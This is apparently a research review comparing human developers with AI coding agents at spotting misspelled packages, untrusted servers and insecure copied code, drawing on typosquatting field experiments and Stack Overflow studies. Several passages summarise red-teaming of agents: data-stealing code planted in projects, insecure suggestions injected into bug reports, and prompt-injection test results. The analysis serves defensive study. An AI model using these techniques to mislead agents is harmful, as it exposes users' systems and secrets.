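For obvious misspellings, a is close to 1, so developers could hardly do better. For vulnerable versions, a is 0, so an agent would do worse than developers who noticed even a few. But developers might notice none, because a reader can't tell from a line such as `requests==2.30.0` that the version has a flaw.

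The pause can also help only when the command itself contains the clue, so it should matter most when the README's install line contains a strange server or a slightly wrong name. When a project hides the server's address in its list of dependencies, the command includes only the list's filename. When a build file redirects the installer, the developer just types `make setup`. In both cases, a developer who hasn't opened the file can't see the clue, and neither can an agent that hasn't opened it.

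Bagmar and Saraf cite other research showing that people also miss bad servers and vulnerable versions, and they say that millions of developers install packages every day without verifying them. Both points suggest that q may be small. Bagmar and Saraf also propose that agents' weaknesses are the reverse of people's, because misspelled names have long fooled people, but they did not give agents and people the same projects. They did not measure what developers do about versions either, although they cite a count of the vulnerable versions that agents and people choose in real projects.

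A person who approves an agent's commands could in principle also provide a pause. If the person and the agent missed things independently, together they would miss (1 − a)(1 − q) of the bad installs. For example, if the agent caught 30% (a = 0.3), as Opus 4.8 did with the local server in Copilot CLI, and the person caught an invented 20% (q = 0.2), together they would catch 44%. But this kind of approval is becoming less common. *Prompt Injection Experiments with Opus-5 in Claude Code* (veganmosfet, 2026) quotes an announcement that from August 14, 2026 new Claude Code sessions would by default run without routine permission prompts. Instead, a second model checks each command and blocks those it judges destructive or aimed outside the user's environment. Bagmar and Saraf collected their data before this change, so their Claude Code results may not describe the product as people now use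 it, even with the same model.

A study that measured q would need little new material. Bagmar and Saraf have promised to publish their test projects, and their script for checking the finished environment would work just as well on a developer's installation. Their malicious test package would put participants at little risk, because it records only the names of settings, not their values, and stores them locally.

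### The user's wording and the user's task

A study of people also has to decide how to phrase the request. In the benchmark *Beyond the Payload* (August 2026), Zhu, Zhao and colleagues tested how much phrasing matters to an agent. They hid data-stealing code in 20 real open-source projects and ran Codex with GPT-5.4 on them 1,920 times, with permission to run any command. To find realistic wordings, they collected requests to coding agents from screenshots on social media and sorted 635 of them by style. A model then rewrote each task in three of the styles: chatty and vague, very brief, and full of typos.

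The wording of the request barely changed how often the agent explicitly flagged the malicious code, which was 12.7% of runs with the plain request and 10.6% to 11.9% with the three other styles. The attack succeeded in 25.8% of runs with the plain request, 20.5% with the very brief one and 26.5% with the one full of typos. Only the very brief style differed significantly from the plain one (p = 0.036), which is weak evidence because three styles were compared with it.

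Zhu and colleagues give two conflicting explanations for the effect of brief requests: the agent explores the project more thoroughly and so discovers the malicious files, or it does less work and stops before reaching them. The second fits their data better, because alerts did not rise with brief requests and the agent in their worked example made 37 tool calls instead of 52. An agent that runs less malicious code only because it does less work is no less credulous.

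The task mattered far more than the wording.

| Task | Attack succeeded | Agent flagged the code |
|---|---|---|
| Run the tests | 45.5% | 9.4% |
| Install and run the project | 24.9% | 34.9% |
| Add a feature | 14.8% | 1.5% |
| Fix a bug | 8.6% | 1.3% |

The difference between running tests and installing remained when Zhu and colleagues counted only runs in which the agent had read the file containing the malicious code. They conclude that an agent inspects a file during setup but treats similar material as something to execute when told to run tests. However, they put the malicious code in a build file for the installation task and in a test file for the other tasks, so the type of file could also explain the difference. Either way, human results on installing packages would be a poor baseline for an agent that runs tests.

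Zhu and colleagues also gave the agent standing security rules, such as a ban on running unverified code. The alert rate rose from 10.5% to 14.8%, but the attack still succeeded in 22.3% of runs, compared with 22.6% without the rules. The researchers suggest that the agent often issued its alerts too late.

The harness seemed to make a large difference here too. With GPT-5.4, the attack succeeded in 22.6% of runs in Codex and 7.7% in OpenCode, an open-source harness. OpenCode's lower rate may partly reflect that it completed fewer tasks, 20.6% compared with 36.8% for Codex. Another table in the paper gives 64.3% for Codex, so the completion figures are uncertain. Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6 had the lowest attack success rate, 6.6%, but Zhu and colleagues record no completed tasks in its 610 scored runs. Claude Code raised alerts no more often than Codex did.

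### Newer models

All of these tests used models from the first half of 2026 or earlier. Anthropic announced two newer models on November 9 (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026). Anthropic's published safety results, which include tests of prompt injection, have mostly improved. According to The Decoder, injected commands failed in all 129 browser scenarios that Anthropic tried on Claude Opus 5.

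The results for coding are less clear. Anthropic reported in June 2026 that Claude Mythos 5 set a record on an outside test of prompt injection but scored between Opus 4.8 and an earlier preview of Mythos on coding and computer-use safety tests. Anthropic also found that Claude Sonnet 5, in use by August 2026, resists prompt injection better than Sonnet 4.6. In security-related tests in Claude Code, Sonnet 5 refused malicious requests much more reliably but also refused more legitimate ones, so part of the improvement may come from a lower threshold for refusing.

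*Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a commentary on Anthropic's report of September 2026, says that resistance to planted commands improved again in that generation, but that Mythos 5.1 is relatively prone to accepting claims of authorisation that it cannot verify. This weakness is closer to credulity than most of what prompt-injection tests measure.

Companies have also reported agents installing bad packages outside test environments. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code*, published on August 30, 2026, describes agents doing so inside corporate networks. Researchers had found that documentation files for AI tools on 120 domains referred to unclaimed names that an attacker could take over. Calculating a rate from such incidents would also require counting the installs that went well.

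A model that resists planted commands may still fail to vet a package server. Opus 4.8 resisted most of the attacks in Gray Swan's test, but in Copilot CLI it missed Bagmar and Saraf's local server in 21 of 30 runs.

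## A field experiment with misspelled package names

Bagmar and Saraf's proposal that agents reverse the human pattern rests partly on the claim that misspelled package names have long fooled people. The best-known evidence is Nikolai Tschacher's bachelor's thesis at the University of Hamburg. In late 2015 and early 2016, Tschacher published harmless packages with names similar to those of popular packages, and they ran 45,334 times on 17,289 distinct hosts. This proves that people, or scripts they wrote, do install packages with the wrong names, but not how often, because nobody counted the correct installs or the people who noticed a wrong name in time.

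### How the experiment worked

Tschacher uploaded about 200 packages to PyPI, npm and RubyGems, the registry for the Ruby language. *Typosquatting in package repositories* (Edge, 2016) gives the example of someone who types `reqeusts` instead of `requests`. Each package contained a small program that ran during installation, sent basic information about the computer to Tschacher's server, and printed a warning that the user had probably chosen the wrong package.

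According to Help Net Security's *How programmers can be tricked into running bad code*, an algorithm generated 166 of the names, covering all possible typos of two package names. Tschacher chose the rest by guessing how people misspell. The program also searched each computer's command history for other wrong names. Tschacher registered some of these for a second phase, and Edge reports that they worked well. Some of the names in these histories were not typing errors. For example, `urllib2` was already part of Python, and `scikit` is a shortened form of `scikit-learn`.

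PyPI accounted for 15,221 of the hosts, RubyGems for 1,631 and npm for 525. Edge suggests the registries' popularity or their users' habits might explain the difference, but the choice of names could matter too. Edge says 43% of the installers had administrator rights, while Help Net Security reports about 50% of confirmed installations. Those rights increase the damage a malicious package could do, but they are weak evidence of whether anyone checked the name.

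Very few users visited the web page linked in the warning. Help Net Security infers from this that most of them never noticed anything suspicious, but the inference is weak. The warning itself explained the mistake, so someone who read it had little reason to follow the link, and nobody watches an automated installation.

### Two missing denominators

An experiment like this could give two rates. One is the share of all installs that go wrong, which requires a count of correct installs. The other is the share of wrong names that people fail to notice before running the command, which requires a count of the ones they did notice. Tschacher had neither count. The table shows the rates that the 45,334 runs would give with invented figures for both counts, treating each run as one install.

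| Correct installs (invented) | Wrong names noticed in time (invented) | Share of installs that went wrong | Share of wrong names that got through |
|---|---|---|---|
| 500,000 | 5,000 | 8.3% | 90% |
| 5 billion | 5,000 | 0.0009% | 90% |
| 5 billion | 5 million | 0.0009% | 0.9% |

In the first row, developers make mistakes often and rarely notice them. In the last row, they make few mistakes relative to the number of installs and notice almost all of them. The experiment can't distinguish between these cases.

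The second rate is the one to compare with Bagmar and Saraf's results, because all their misspelling tests contained a wrong name. Even a perfect count of correct installs would therefore not provide the human baseline. Registry logs might help a little. Tschacher suggested that registries search them for likely typos, and they could also show how often a request for a wrong name is soon followed by a request for the right one. They would still miss anyone who corrected the name before pressing Enter.

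The number of runs also depends on how many misspelled names Tschacher registered. If he had registered another hundred common misspellings, the number would have gone up even if developers were just as careful.

A typing slip also isn't a sign of credulity in itself. Someone who types `reqeusts` thinks they have asked for the usual package and hasn't decided to trust a stranger's. The slip does show a lack of vetting, since they would have caught it by rereading the command. But the same developer might be suspicious of an unfamiliar package named in a README.

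### Runs, machines and people

The 45,334 runs include repeats of the same mistake. *Typosquatting Package Managers* (2016) quotes Tschacher as explaining that his server received this many requests, and that they outnumber the hosts mainly because pip ran each package's setup file twice. Bagmar and Saraf describe the figure as installations over two weeks, but Edge says the two phases lasted about two months in total.

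The number of hosts is a better guide to the number of people, but still a rough one. Tschacher identified hosts by internet address, but a whole office can share one address, and a cloud service may use a new one for each job. Many companies have servers that reinstall a project's dependencies whenever its code changes, so one person's typo in a dependency file can produce hundreds of installs. About 10% of the addresses that Tschacher could match to a hostname belonged to Amazon's cloud service. Some of the installs from these addresses may have come from automated builds, and others from people working on rented machines.

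Mirrors, which are copies of a registry, are a bigger problem for studies that count downloads. *SpellBound* (Taylor, Vaidya and colleagues, 2020) cites an estimate by npm's creators that a package can receive up to 50 downloads a day without any developer installing it. Tschacher counted only packages that ran, so his figures would exclude mirrors that merely copied the files but include security scanners that ran the packages.

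### Later field evidence

Taylor and colleagues also found a misspelled package that developers were using by accident. The npm package `loadsh` had 2,593 downloads a week, compared with 27.7 million for the real `lodash`, or about one for every 10,700. The `lodash` count provides a denominator, but both counts include automated downloads. Another 63 packages depended on `loadsh`, so anyone who installed one of them received `loadsh` without typing its name.

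The researchers emailed the maintainers of packages that used `loadsh`. The three who replied all said they had meant to use `lodash`. Many of the projects had contained the mistake for more than a year. `loadsh` was an exact copy of an older version of `lodash`, so nothing broke to reveal the error. Confirmation from the people responsible is better evidence of human error than a download count, but these replies leave out everyone who spotted the mistake early.

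*Typosquatting NLTK on PyPI* shows how much the choice of denominator matters for a single typo. Its author, who works in security, typed `ntlk` instead of `nltk`, a language-processing library, three times in a row, then registered the wrong name with a package that stopped the installation and gave the correct command. In about seven months, the package recorded 28,839 installs from 10,938 addresses, and 76% of the installs came from home or other consumer internet connections.

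At the time, `nltk` had about two million downloads a week, or roughly 61 million over seven months, so the typo accounted for about 0.05% of downloads. But most of those downloads were automated. On Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers, `ntlk` appeared 244 times and `nltk` 21,228 times. That is a rate of about 1.1%, more than twenty times the first estimate. Neither figure measures the share of typed commands that contained the typo, and `ntlk` is probably an unusually easy mistake to make, since the author also kept making it when saying the name aloud.

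In July 2018, William Bengtson tried a much larger set of names, which he made by removing the hyphens and underscores from the names of popular PyPI packages. *Further analysis of PyPI typosquatting* (Edge, 2020) quotes a total of 530,950 install commands for 1,131 packages in just over two years, excluding mirrors. The quoted claim that 530,950 machines could have been compromised assumes one attempt per machine. Bengtson's packages stopped with an error, so a person or an automated build might well have tried again.

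Meyers and Tozer, in *Bewear! Python Typosquatting Is About More Than Typos*, call Bengtson's count a lower bound on how susceptible PyPI's users are, because missing separators are only one way to get a name wrong. That is reasonable for the total number of wrong installs, but the count doesn't give a rate. It averages about 470 installs per name over the period, or less than one a day. Without knowing how often people typed the correct names by hand, we can't tell whether that is a lot.

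Neupane, Holmes and colleagues (2023), in *Beyond Typosquatting*, counted attacks instead of installs. They sorted 1,232 documented cases into 13 categories and found that 82% relied on name confusions such as reordered words or changed separators, rather than simple typing errors. The share drops to 43% without one campaign that mass-produced 722 Ruby names by changing separators. These percentages describe what attackers tried, and they count each attack equally no matter how many people it fooled.

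Neupane and colleagues also surveyed people with software development experience about pairs of similar names. For their most effective detection rule, participants rated 77% of the pairs as potentially or highly confusing, but only 18% as highly confusing. This survey does have a denominator, the number of pairs rated. But judging whether two names could be confused is different from noticing a wrong name during an install, when the correct one isn't there for comparison.

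### Names of packages that do not exist

Language models make a related mistake when they recommend packages that don't exist. In an attack called slopsquatting, an attacker registers such a name and waits for someone to install the package. Spracklen and colleagues (2025) measured the problem in 576,000 code samples from 16 models released between mid-2023 and mid-2024. On average, 5.2% of the packages mentioned by commercial models did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open-source models.

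*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) gave the same prompts to five newer models in April 2026 and checked the names against the live registries that November.

| Model, tested in April 2026 | Package mentions that named a nonexistent package |
|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 3.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4.8% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 4.8% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 5.0% |

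The best of these models did about as well as GPT-4 Turbo, the best model in the earlier study, which had a rate of 3.6%. The rates were lower for questions taken from Stack Overflow (2.3% to 3.1% across the two sets) than for questions written by a language model (4.8% to 5.4%). Earlier versions of Churilov's paper reported higher rates, partly because correct import statements were counted as errors when a Python package had one name for installation and another for use in code.

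Some locally run models may do worse. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) describes 385 runs of such models, in which a classifier flagged 179 of 823 package names as hallucinated. Only half of the flagged names were missing from PyPI, so about 11% of the 823 names were truly nonexistent. The other flagged packages existed but had suspicious-looking details. One was `skimage`, which people also confuse with `scikit-image`.

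Unlike the field experiments, these studies have a denominator, but they measured models answering questions rather than agents installing packages. An agent that tries to install a package with an invented name gets an error and can look for the right name, unless someone has registered the invented one. Such registrations seem to be rare so far. Churilov found that 25 of 2,282 invented names had been registered within about six months, at least one of them with malware.

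People also ask for packages that don't exist. Tschacher's command histories included some wrong names that nobody had registered, and a developer who guesses `scikit` is doing something similar to a model that invents a plausible name. But nobody seems to have given Churilov's prompts to developers working from memory, so there is no human rate to compare with the 3.6% to 5.0%.

### Whether agents reverse the human pattern

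Agents would reverse the human pattern only if people were better at spotting untrusted servers than wrong names. The field experiments don't measure how well people spot untrusted servers, because every package in them was on an official registry. They show that people make mistakes with names, but not that people miss a larger share of wrong names than agents do.

Suppose, using invented figures, that developers caught 60% of the wrong names in a set of READMEs and 10% of the untrusted servers. They would do worse on names than most of Bagmar and Saraf's agents, but like the agents, they would find names easier to catch than servers. The large number of people who have installed misspelled packages is compatible with this.

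The two studies also concern different mistakes. Bagmar and Saraf supplied every wrong name, either in a project's files or in an error message, so their agents had to notice somebody else's error. People could install Tschacher's packages because they mistyped a name, misremembered it or copied it from a faulty source, and his counts don't separate these causes. Some people who installed `ntlk` may have copied it from one of those 244 mentions on Stack Overflow.

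A misspelled package name can easily end up in documentation that other people follow. Bagmar and Saraf found `tdqm`, a misspelling of the popular package `tqdm`, in more than 960 dependency files on GitHub. They also report that `sklearn`, a placeholder that tells users to install `scikit-learn`, had about 1.8 million downloads in one month in mid-2026. Few of those downloads can be typing errors, because programmers use the name `sklearn` in their code. Some may not come from people at all. *Typosquatting in package managers* (2025) lists language models alongside typing and copied tutorials as sources of wrong names, so a new field experiment would probably count agents as well as people. Tschacher's experiment has the advantage of predating coding agents.

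Agents look less reliable when they have to supply package names themselves. Sonnet 4.6 caught every misspelling that Bagmar and Saraf planted in a project's dependency file, but about 4% of the packages it mentioned in Churilov's test did not exist. People and agents share at least one weakness, since some of the agents missed the same kind of error, a missing separator, that caught Bengtson's users.

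Bagmar and Saraf's test projects could show how often developers copy a wrong name. To measure typing errors, researchers could tell developers aloud which library to install and record what they type. The recording would include misspellings corrected before the developer pressed Enter, which don't appear in registry data.

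## Experiments on developers who copy code from Stack Overflow and official documentation

A developer who copies code from Stack Overflow is taking someone's advice, unlike one who types `reqeusts` by mistake. That advice can be insecure even when its author meant to help. Researchers have watched developers copy code in experiments and have searched published apps for the copied code. Their results give a human baseline for relying on honest but insecure advice, though nobody seems to have given coding agents the same tasks.

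### Four tasks and four sources

Acar, Backes and colleagues (2017), in *How Internet Resources Might Be Helping You Develop Faster but Less Securely*, describe an experiment they first published in 2016. They asked 54 people with some Android experience to finish parts of an app. Most (89%) were students, and 14 worked or had recently worked as programmers. Each person had 20 to 30 minutes for each of four tasks, and every task could be completed with either secure or insecure code.

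In one task, participants had to switch the app to an encrypted connection, but the server's certificate, which proves its identity, carried the wrong name. A secure solution made an exception for this one certificate, while an insecure one accepted any certificate, so an attacker could pose as the server. The other tasks were to store a password on the phone, open a service to the developer's other apps, and make a button dial a phone number. Insecure solutions let other apps read the password, opened the service to every app, or requested a permission the app didn't need.

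Each participant could consult only Stack Overflow, only the official Android documentation, only two books, or anything they liked. The researchers checked beforehand that each source contained a secure solution to every task. The instructions did not mention security, though participants could have inferred its relevance from a task about passwords or encrypted connections.

| Permitted source | Working solutions | Secure | Insecure | Secure share of working solutions |
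|---|---|---|---|---|
| Stack Overflow | 35 | 18 | 17 | 51.4% |
| Free choice | 29 | 19 | 10 | 65.5% |
| Two books | 37 | 27 | 10 | 73.0% |
| Official documentation | 21 | 18 | 3 | 85.7% |

Participants with Stack Overflow got 67% of their tasks working, and those with books 66%. Those with the official documentation had the highest share of secure solutions but got only 40% of their tasks working, the lowest of any group.

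The Stack Overflow and documentation groups were about the same size, and each produced 18 secure working solutions. On the remaining tasks, the Stack Overflow group often wrote insecure code, while the documentation group mostly produced nothing that worked, and so wrote much less insecure code. The book group produced 27 secure solutions, but only one person in the free-choice group opened a book.

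Many developers in the free-choice group started with the official documentation. If they still had nothing working as time ran out, they often pasted a snippet, a short piece of ready-made code, from Stack Overflow.

The secure share also excludes participants who gave up. In the certificate task, 20 participants mentioned security, and nine of them later gave up because the task seemed too difficult or too long for a study. Giving up may be safer than accepting every certificate, but it counts only as a failure to produce working code. An agent that refused an insecure shortcut and left the task unfinished would also be left out of the security figures.

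### What the participants noticed

Acar and colleagues asked participants to think aloud. In 79% of tasks, participants never mentioned security, and only four people used "secure" or "security" in a search. When the researchers asked afterwards, participants said they had considered security in 60% of tasks. Some may have thought about it silently, and others may have remembered more caution than they had shown. The 79% figure is the better measure of how developers behave when nobody has asked them about security.

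The four groups' code differed in security, although the groups did not differ significantly in how often they mentioned security. The sources they used probably explain most of the gap, rather than how careful the developers were. A human baseline therefore has to specify the source as well as the developers, because the same kind of developer looks more careful with the official documentation than with Stack Overflow.

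Participants seem to have done little vetting of the code they found. Of the 41 relevant threads they visited, 20 contained ready-to-use code: seven had only secure code, ten had only insecure code and three had both. Someone who copied from one of those 20 at random would get secure code between 35% and 50% of the time, and the Stack Overflow group produced secure code 51% of the time. The comparison is rough because it gives every thread equal weight and some participants wrote their own code. But if participants had been good at rejecting insecure snippets, their share of secure code should have been well above what random copying would give.

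Some participants used snippets they knew were insecure. One said "I know this is a very bad idea" and then used the snippet. That may be a sensible way to finish on time when the app is a laboratory exercise with no users. The 17 insecure solutions therefore reflect deliberate shortcuts as well as misplaced trust.

The professionals finished more tasks, but their working solutions were about as secure as the others' (69% were secure on average, compared with 66%). With only 14 professionals spread over four sources, the study could easily have missed a moderate difference.

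### Copied code in published apps

To find out how much of this code reaches real users, *Stack Overflow Considered Harmful?* (Fischer, Böttinger et al., 2017) searched 1.3 million free Android apps for security-related snippets from Stack Overflow's Android threads. A trained classifier labeled each snippet secure or insecure. Matching code appeared in 200,672 apps (15.4%), and 196,403 of those (97.9%) contained at least one insecure snippet.

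The 97.9% figure covers only apps with copied code, so it leaves out every developer who read an insecure snippet and rejected it. It therefore doesn't measure how often developers fail to vet code. Suppose 1,000 developers read an insecure snippet, 950 spot the problem and write their own code, and 50 copy it. One other developer copies a secure snippet. A scan would find copied code in 51 apps, 98% of them insecure, even though only 5% of the developers who saw the insecure snippet used it.

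The figure also depends heavily on one piece of code, which matched 180,388 apps. This component should check certificates, but it has been left empty, so it approves all of them. Without it, the number of apps with an insecure match drops from 196,403 to 43,941. An empty component has almost no code to compare, so Fischer and colleagues matched it by the names of its functions. Java fixes those names, so a developer who left the same functions empty without visiting Stack Overflow would count as having copied them. An outside library with this code could also put it in thousands of apps whose developers never saw it.

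Even when the code is distinctive, a match doesn't show whether it was copied from Stack Overflow into the app or from the app to Stack Overflow. Code in questions matched code in 198,347 apps, while code in answers matched only 40,786. People often post their own code when they ask for help, so some of the matching code may have come from the apps. The researchers concede that they can't fully prove where the code came from, but they consider Stack Overflow very likely to be the source, partly because snippets with more views also appeared in more apps.

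The results varied by topic. For encrypted connections, 183,268 apps had an insecure match and 441 a secure one. For symmetric encryption, which uses the same key to encrypt and decrypt data, the numbers were nearly equal (21,239 insecure and 19,452 secure). For hash functions, only 14 apps had an insecure match, while 4,012 had a secure one. A general reluctance to check code wouldn't produce differences this large. The supply of snippets and how hard the secure version is to write probably matter more.

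Insecure snippets with a warning in the comments appeared in more apps than those without one. Developers may have ignored the warnings, but popular snippets also get more comments and are copied more often.

The content of Stack Overflow has changed since then. *Stack Overflow Meets Replication* (Jallow and Bugiel, 2025) repeated six security studies of the site on newer data, and four gave significantly different results. The two with stable results both concerned the misuse of cryptography in Java, and one was the 2017 study of Android apps.

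### Votes and search rankings

A developer who can't judge a snippet directly may rely on other people's opinions. Chen, Fischer and colleagues (2019), in *How Reliable is the Crowdsourced Knowledge of Security Implementation?*, tested whether this is reliable. They labelled 1,429 answers containing security-related Java code and found that 644 (45%) were insecure. They sampled only code that appeared on Stack Overflow more than once in similar form, so the share may differ across the site as a whole. In the 2017 study, about 31% of the distinct snippets in Android answers were insecure.

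An answer's vote score seems to be almost unrelated to its security. Insecure answers had a higher average score than secure ones (14 compared with 5), but the difference was nowhere near significant in a test that compares ranks (p = 0.97), so a small number of very popular answers probably raised the average.

An "accepted" mark, by which the asker endorses an answer, is no better. In Chen and colleagues' sample, a developer who used only accepted answers would reject 405 of the 644 insecure answers (63%) and 488 of the 785 secure ones (62%), giving a sensitivity, d′, of about 0.02. Using only answers from "trusted users", who have at least 20,000 reputation points, would raise d′ to about 0.3, but the developer would then reject 83% of the secure answers too.

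A developer who vets every answer and distrusts most of them isn't credulous in the ordinary sense, even if the evidence they use is nearly worthless. An agent that chose packages by download counts or GitHub stars could have the same problem.

Search engines affect which answers developers see. Fischer, Stachelscheid and Grossklags (2021), in *The Effect of Google Search on Software Security*, had 192 developers search for help with encryption tasks. They estimated a 22.8% chance that at least one of the top three results led to a Stack Overflow page whose top answer was insecure. The chance for a page with a secure top answer was 9.2%. Since the top three results received 79% of the clicks, their order could matter a good deal. The 22.8% figure measures exposure to insecure answers, not what developers do after opening the page.

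The researchers then tested the effect of search result order. They built a search engine that moved secure examples up and insecure ones down, and randomly assigned 218 developers to use this ranking or the original one. Participants wrote three short encryption programs, and neither the invitation nor the tasks mentioned security.

| | Original ranking | Reordered results |
|---|---|---|
| Labelled results that were insecure | 68.8% | 17.3% |
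| Clicks on labelled results that went to insecure pages | 84.3% | about 33% |
| Secure solutions out of 3, participants who searched less | about 1.6 | about 1.6 |
| Secure solutions out of 3, participants who searched more | about 1.6 | about 1.9 |

Reordering had no significant effect on security across the whole group. Its benefit increased significantly with the number of searches (p < 0.05), which makes sense because people who rarely used the search engine had little chance to benefit. But participants chose how much to search, and only 218 of the 827 who began the study finished it, so this benefit is less certain than a simple difference between randomised groups would be. Participants could also have used another search engine without the researchers knowing.

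Developers in both groups didn't avoid insecure pages, which received more clicks than their share of the results. Even when the search engine ranked these pages lower, they received about a third of the clicks while making up about a sixth of the labelled results. Their titles may have matched the task better, or their code may have looked simpler.

With the original ranking, participants produced on average about 1.6 secure solutions out of 3, or roughly half. That is close to the 51% for Stack Overflow in the 2016 experiment, even though the tasks differed and most participants were professionals. Half is therefore a reasonable first guess for the share of secure solutions among unprimed developers who look up security-related code, but not among developers who follow a README.

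### Why developers reuse insecure code

In *A Qualitative Investigation of Insecure Code Propagation from Online Forums*, Bai, Akgul and Mazurek (2019) looked for GitHub projects containing insecure cryptographic code that matched Stack Overflow posts, surveyed 133 of the developers and interviewed 15. Twelve of the interviewees said they had used online forums for the project, and eight of those twelve had not considered security when deciding whether to use the code.

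The other four had considered it and still ended up with insecure code. The eight seem credulous, while the four apparently looked for evidence but couldn't interpret it. The two failures look identical in the finished project, so neither the scan of Android apps nor a test that only inspects an agent's final code can tell them apart.

Some of the developers' reasons involve neither failure. Seven interviewees said the weakness didn't matter in their project. One had used encryption only to give each subscriber to a video game cheat a unique identifier, and argued that cracking it would achieve nothing. After the interviewers explained the weaknesses, two developers fixed them, one deleted the project, one closed their GitHub account, and the other 11 changed nothing. Some of the reasons may be excuses, as Bai and colleagues suggest, but working developers do consider how much a flaw matters,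 while benchmarks usually count every flaw the same.

People also describe themselves as more careful than they are. In the survey, only 7 of 43 open-source developers who looked up security code on Stack Overflow said they never checked its security, compared with 8 of 12 in the interviews. The two samples differ, but a questionnaire about vetting would clearly be a poor substitute for watching people work. The study also can't show how common insecure copying is, because all its participants came from projects that contained insecure code.

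### Honest advice and hostile advice

The advice in all these studies came from people who were mostly trying to help. Chen and colleagues found one user who posted nine insecure snippets, but no evidence that this user or anyone else intended to mislead. The studies therefore give a baseline for how often unprimed developers rely on honest but insecure advice. The closest match among Bagmar and Saraf's scenarios is the README that names a vulnerable version, because an honest author could easily have written it.

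These experiments don't measure resistance to a deliberate attacker, who might fool developers more or less often than honest bad advice does. An attacker can try several wordings and keep the most persuasive, or add a false explanation for a suspicious step. But an attack may contain clues that honest bad advice lacks. For example, anyone can notice that a package comes from an unknown server, but recognising a weak encryption setting takes specialist knowledge. The developer also has more at stake, because a malicious package can steal their own passwords within seconds, while an insecure snippet mainly endangers the app's future users.

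An agent may respond to a piece of text in the same way whether or not its writer meant harm. In *When "Correct" Is Not Safe*, Peng, Song and colleagues (2025) added insecure suggestions to bug reports and asked agents to fix the bugs. An attacker could have written the suggestions, or an honest developer could have copied them from a bad source. In one set of tests, following the suggestion would expose sensitive information to outsiders. With the OpenHands harness, GPT-5 mini produced a working fix with this flaw in 40.7% of cases and Claude Sonnet 4 in 55.6%, counting only bugs that the agent could fix without the suggestion. In a simpler harness with no suggestion, 4.5% of GPT-5 mini's working fixes and 4.3% of Claude Sonnet 4's had some vulnerability.

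Both models date from 2025. The test also differs from copying code from Stack Overflow because the suggestion is part of the request. Developers choose the snippets they find online, but may feel obliged to follow an insecure instruction in a bug report.

### Tests of agents with insecure code

In an earlier test, *Do LLMs Consider Security?* (Sajadi, Le and colleagues, 2025) gave 300 Stack Overflow questions containing vulnerable code to GPT-4, Claude 3 and Llama 3, which were released in 2023 and 2024. The models warned about the vulnerability in only 12.6% to 40% of cases, depending on the model and the set of questions. One question was about stray characters in a file, but its code also switched off certificate checking. All three models fixed the stray characters and ignored the disabled certificate checking.

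Sajadi and colleagues' study doesn't provide a human detection rate to compare with the models'. They chose half the questions because someone on Stack Overflow had pointed out the flaw and half because nobody had, which fixed the human rate at 50%. The models were also answering questions rather than using answers, as developers do when they copy code. *Inference-Time Safety For Code LLMs Via Retrieval-Augmented Revision* (2026) comes closer to the developers' task. Its system shows a model security discussions from Stack Overflow about code like its own, and the model can then revise its code or leave it unchanged. But those discussions contain warnings, so they prime the model to look for flaws.

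The closest counterpart for current agents is *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026), in which agents were given identical programming tasks in two versions of a project, one with secure code nearby and one with insecure code. In 20 pairs of tasks from real C and C++ projects, agents had to fill in missing code where a mistake could corrupt memory. The five models included Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, both from autumn 2026. On average, the share of secure solutions was 35.4% lower when similar code elsewhere in the project was insecure.

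The effect was much smaller when agents using Claude Opus 5, GPT-5.6 Sol or GLM 5.3 wrote a new web application beside finished ones that they didn't need. When the existing applications were insecure, the share of new applications that were both correct and secure was 3.4% lower on average than when there were no existing applications. Telling agents to follow the existing style strengthened the influence of insecure code, and telling them to be careful about security weakened it without removing it.

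When Sun and colleagues asked the agents to review their own vulnerable code, the agents identified the flaw 69.9% of the time. When asked instead to explain the code, they attributed the vulnerable choice to similar code elsewhere in the project 76.5% of the time. Like Acar's participants, the agents showed more concern for security when asked directly than they had in their work. However, following a project's existing code is normally good practice, and nobody had offered that code to the agents as advice.

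The 35.4% and the 34-point gap between Acar's documentation and Stack Overflow groups measure different things, though the numbers are close. Acar and colleagues divided secure solutions by working solutions, while Sun and colleagues divided solutions that were both correct and secure by all attempts. By Sun's measure, Acar's two groups are almost equal, because each produced 18 correct and secure solutions from a similar number of attempts. A matched comparison would have to use the same denominator for people and agents.

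### A matched test

The 2016 design would work for agents with some changes. Researchers could save copies of the permitted pages and let both people and agents search only those. They would need new tasks, because the old ones have been public for a decade and a model may have learned the solutions. Agents can also complete many tasks without looking anything up, so the test should include a condition with no source. Otherwise, an agent that ignored an insecure page and answered from memory would appear to have detected the problem.

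Each page should have two versions, one with a secure snippet and one with an insecure snippet, with the same votes and surrounding text. Half the participants would see each version. This design would measure how often participants mistake secure code for insecure code (false alarms), which the human studies do not measure. The researchers would have to ask why people and agents changed a snippet, because rewriting secure code to fit a project's style is not a false alarm.

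The results should give secure, insecure and unfinished solutions as shares of all attempts, because agents may finish far more tasks than people do in half an hour. Suppose an agent finished all 52 tasks that a group of 13 people would attempt, and 80% of its solutions were secure. Its secure share would be lower than the documentation group's 85.7%, but it would produce about 42 secure solutions and ten insecure ones, compared with the group's 18 and three.

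Time limits are harder to match between people and agents. Acar's free-choice participants often turned to Stack Overflow snippets as the deadline approached, so some of their insecure code was due to time pressure. An agent that can read dozens of pages in half an hour is under little pressure from the same limit. Limiting the number of pages or commands might create similar pressure. Testing both people and agents with and without a tight limit would show how much of the difference between them comes from haste.

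## Evidence on people who follow tutorials and paste installation commands

A Stack Overflow answer usually supplies one piece of code that the developer must fit into a program. Tutorials and installation pages, like READMEs, give steps to carry out as written, so the people who follow them are a closer match for an agent setting up a project. Researchers have studied the code these people write, the guides they choose and the checks they make on downloads, but have paid much less attention to how they decide whether to run a pasted command.

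### Projects that resemble flawed tutorials

Unruh, Shastry and colleagues (2017), in *Leveraging Flawed Tutorials for Seeding Large-Scale Web Vulnerability Discovery*, looked for traces of insecure tutorials in public code written in PHP, a language for websites. Their method had four steps:

1. They typed six queries, such as "php mysql user query", into Google and reviewed the top five results for each. Nine of the 30 tutorials contained vulnerable code.
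2. They turned the vulnerable code into templates, which ignored the names of variables but kept the order of operations and the flow of data between them.
3. They downloaded 64,415 PHP projects from GitHub and searched them automatically for code that fitted a template.
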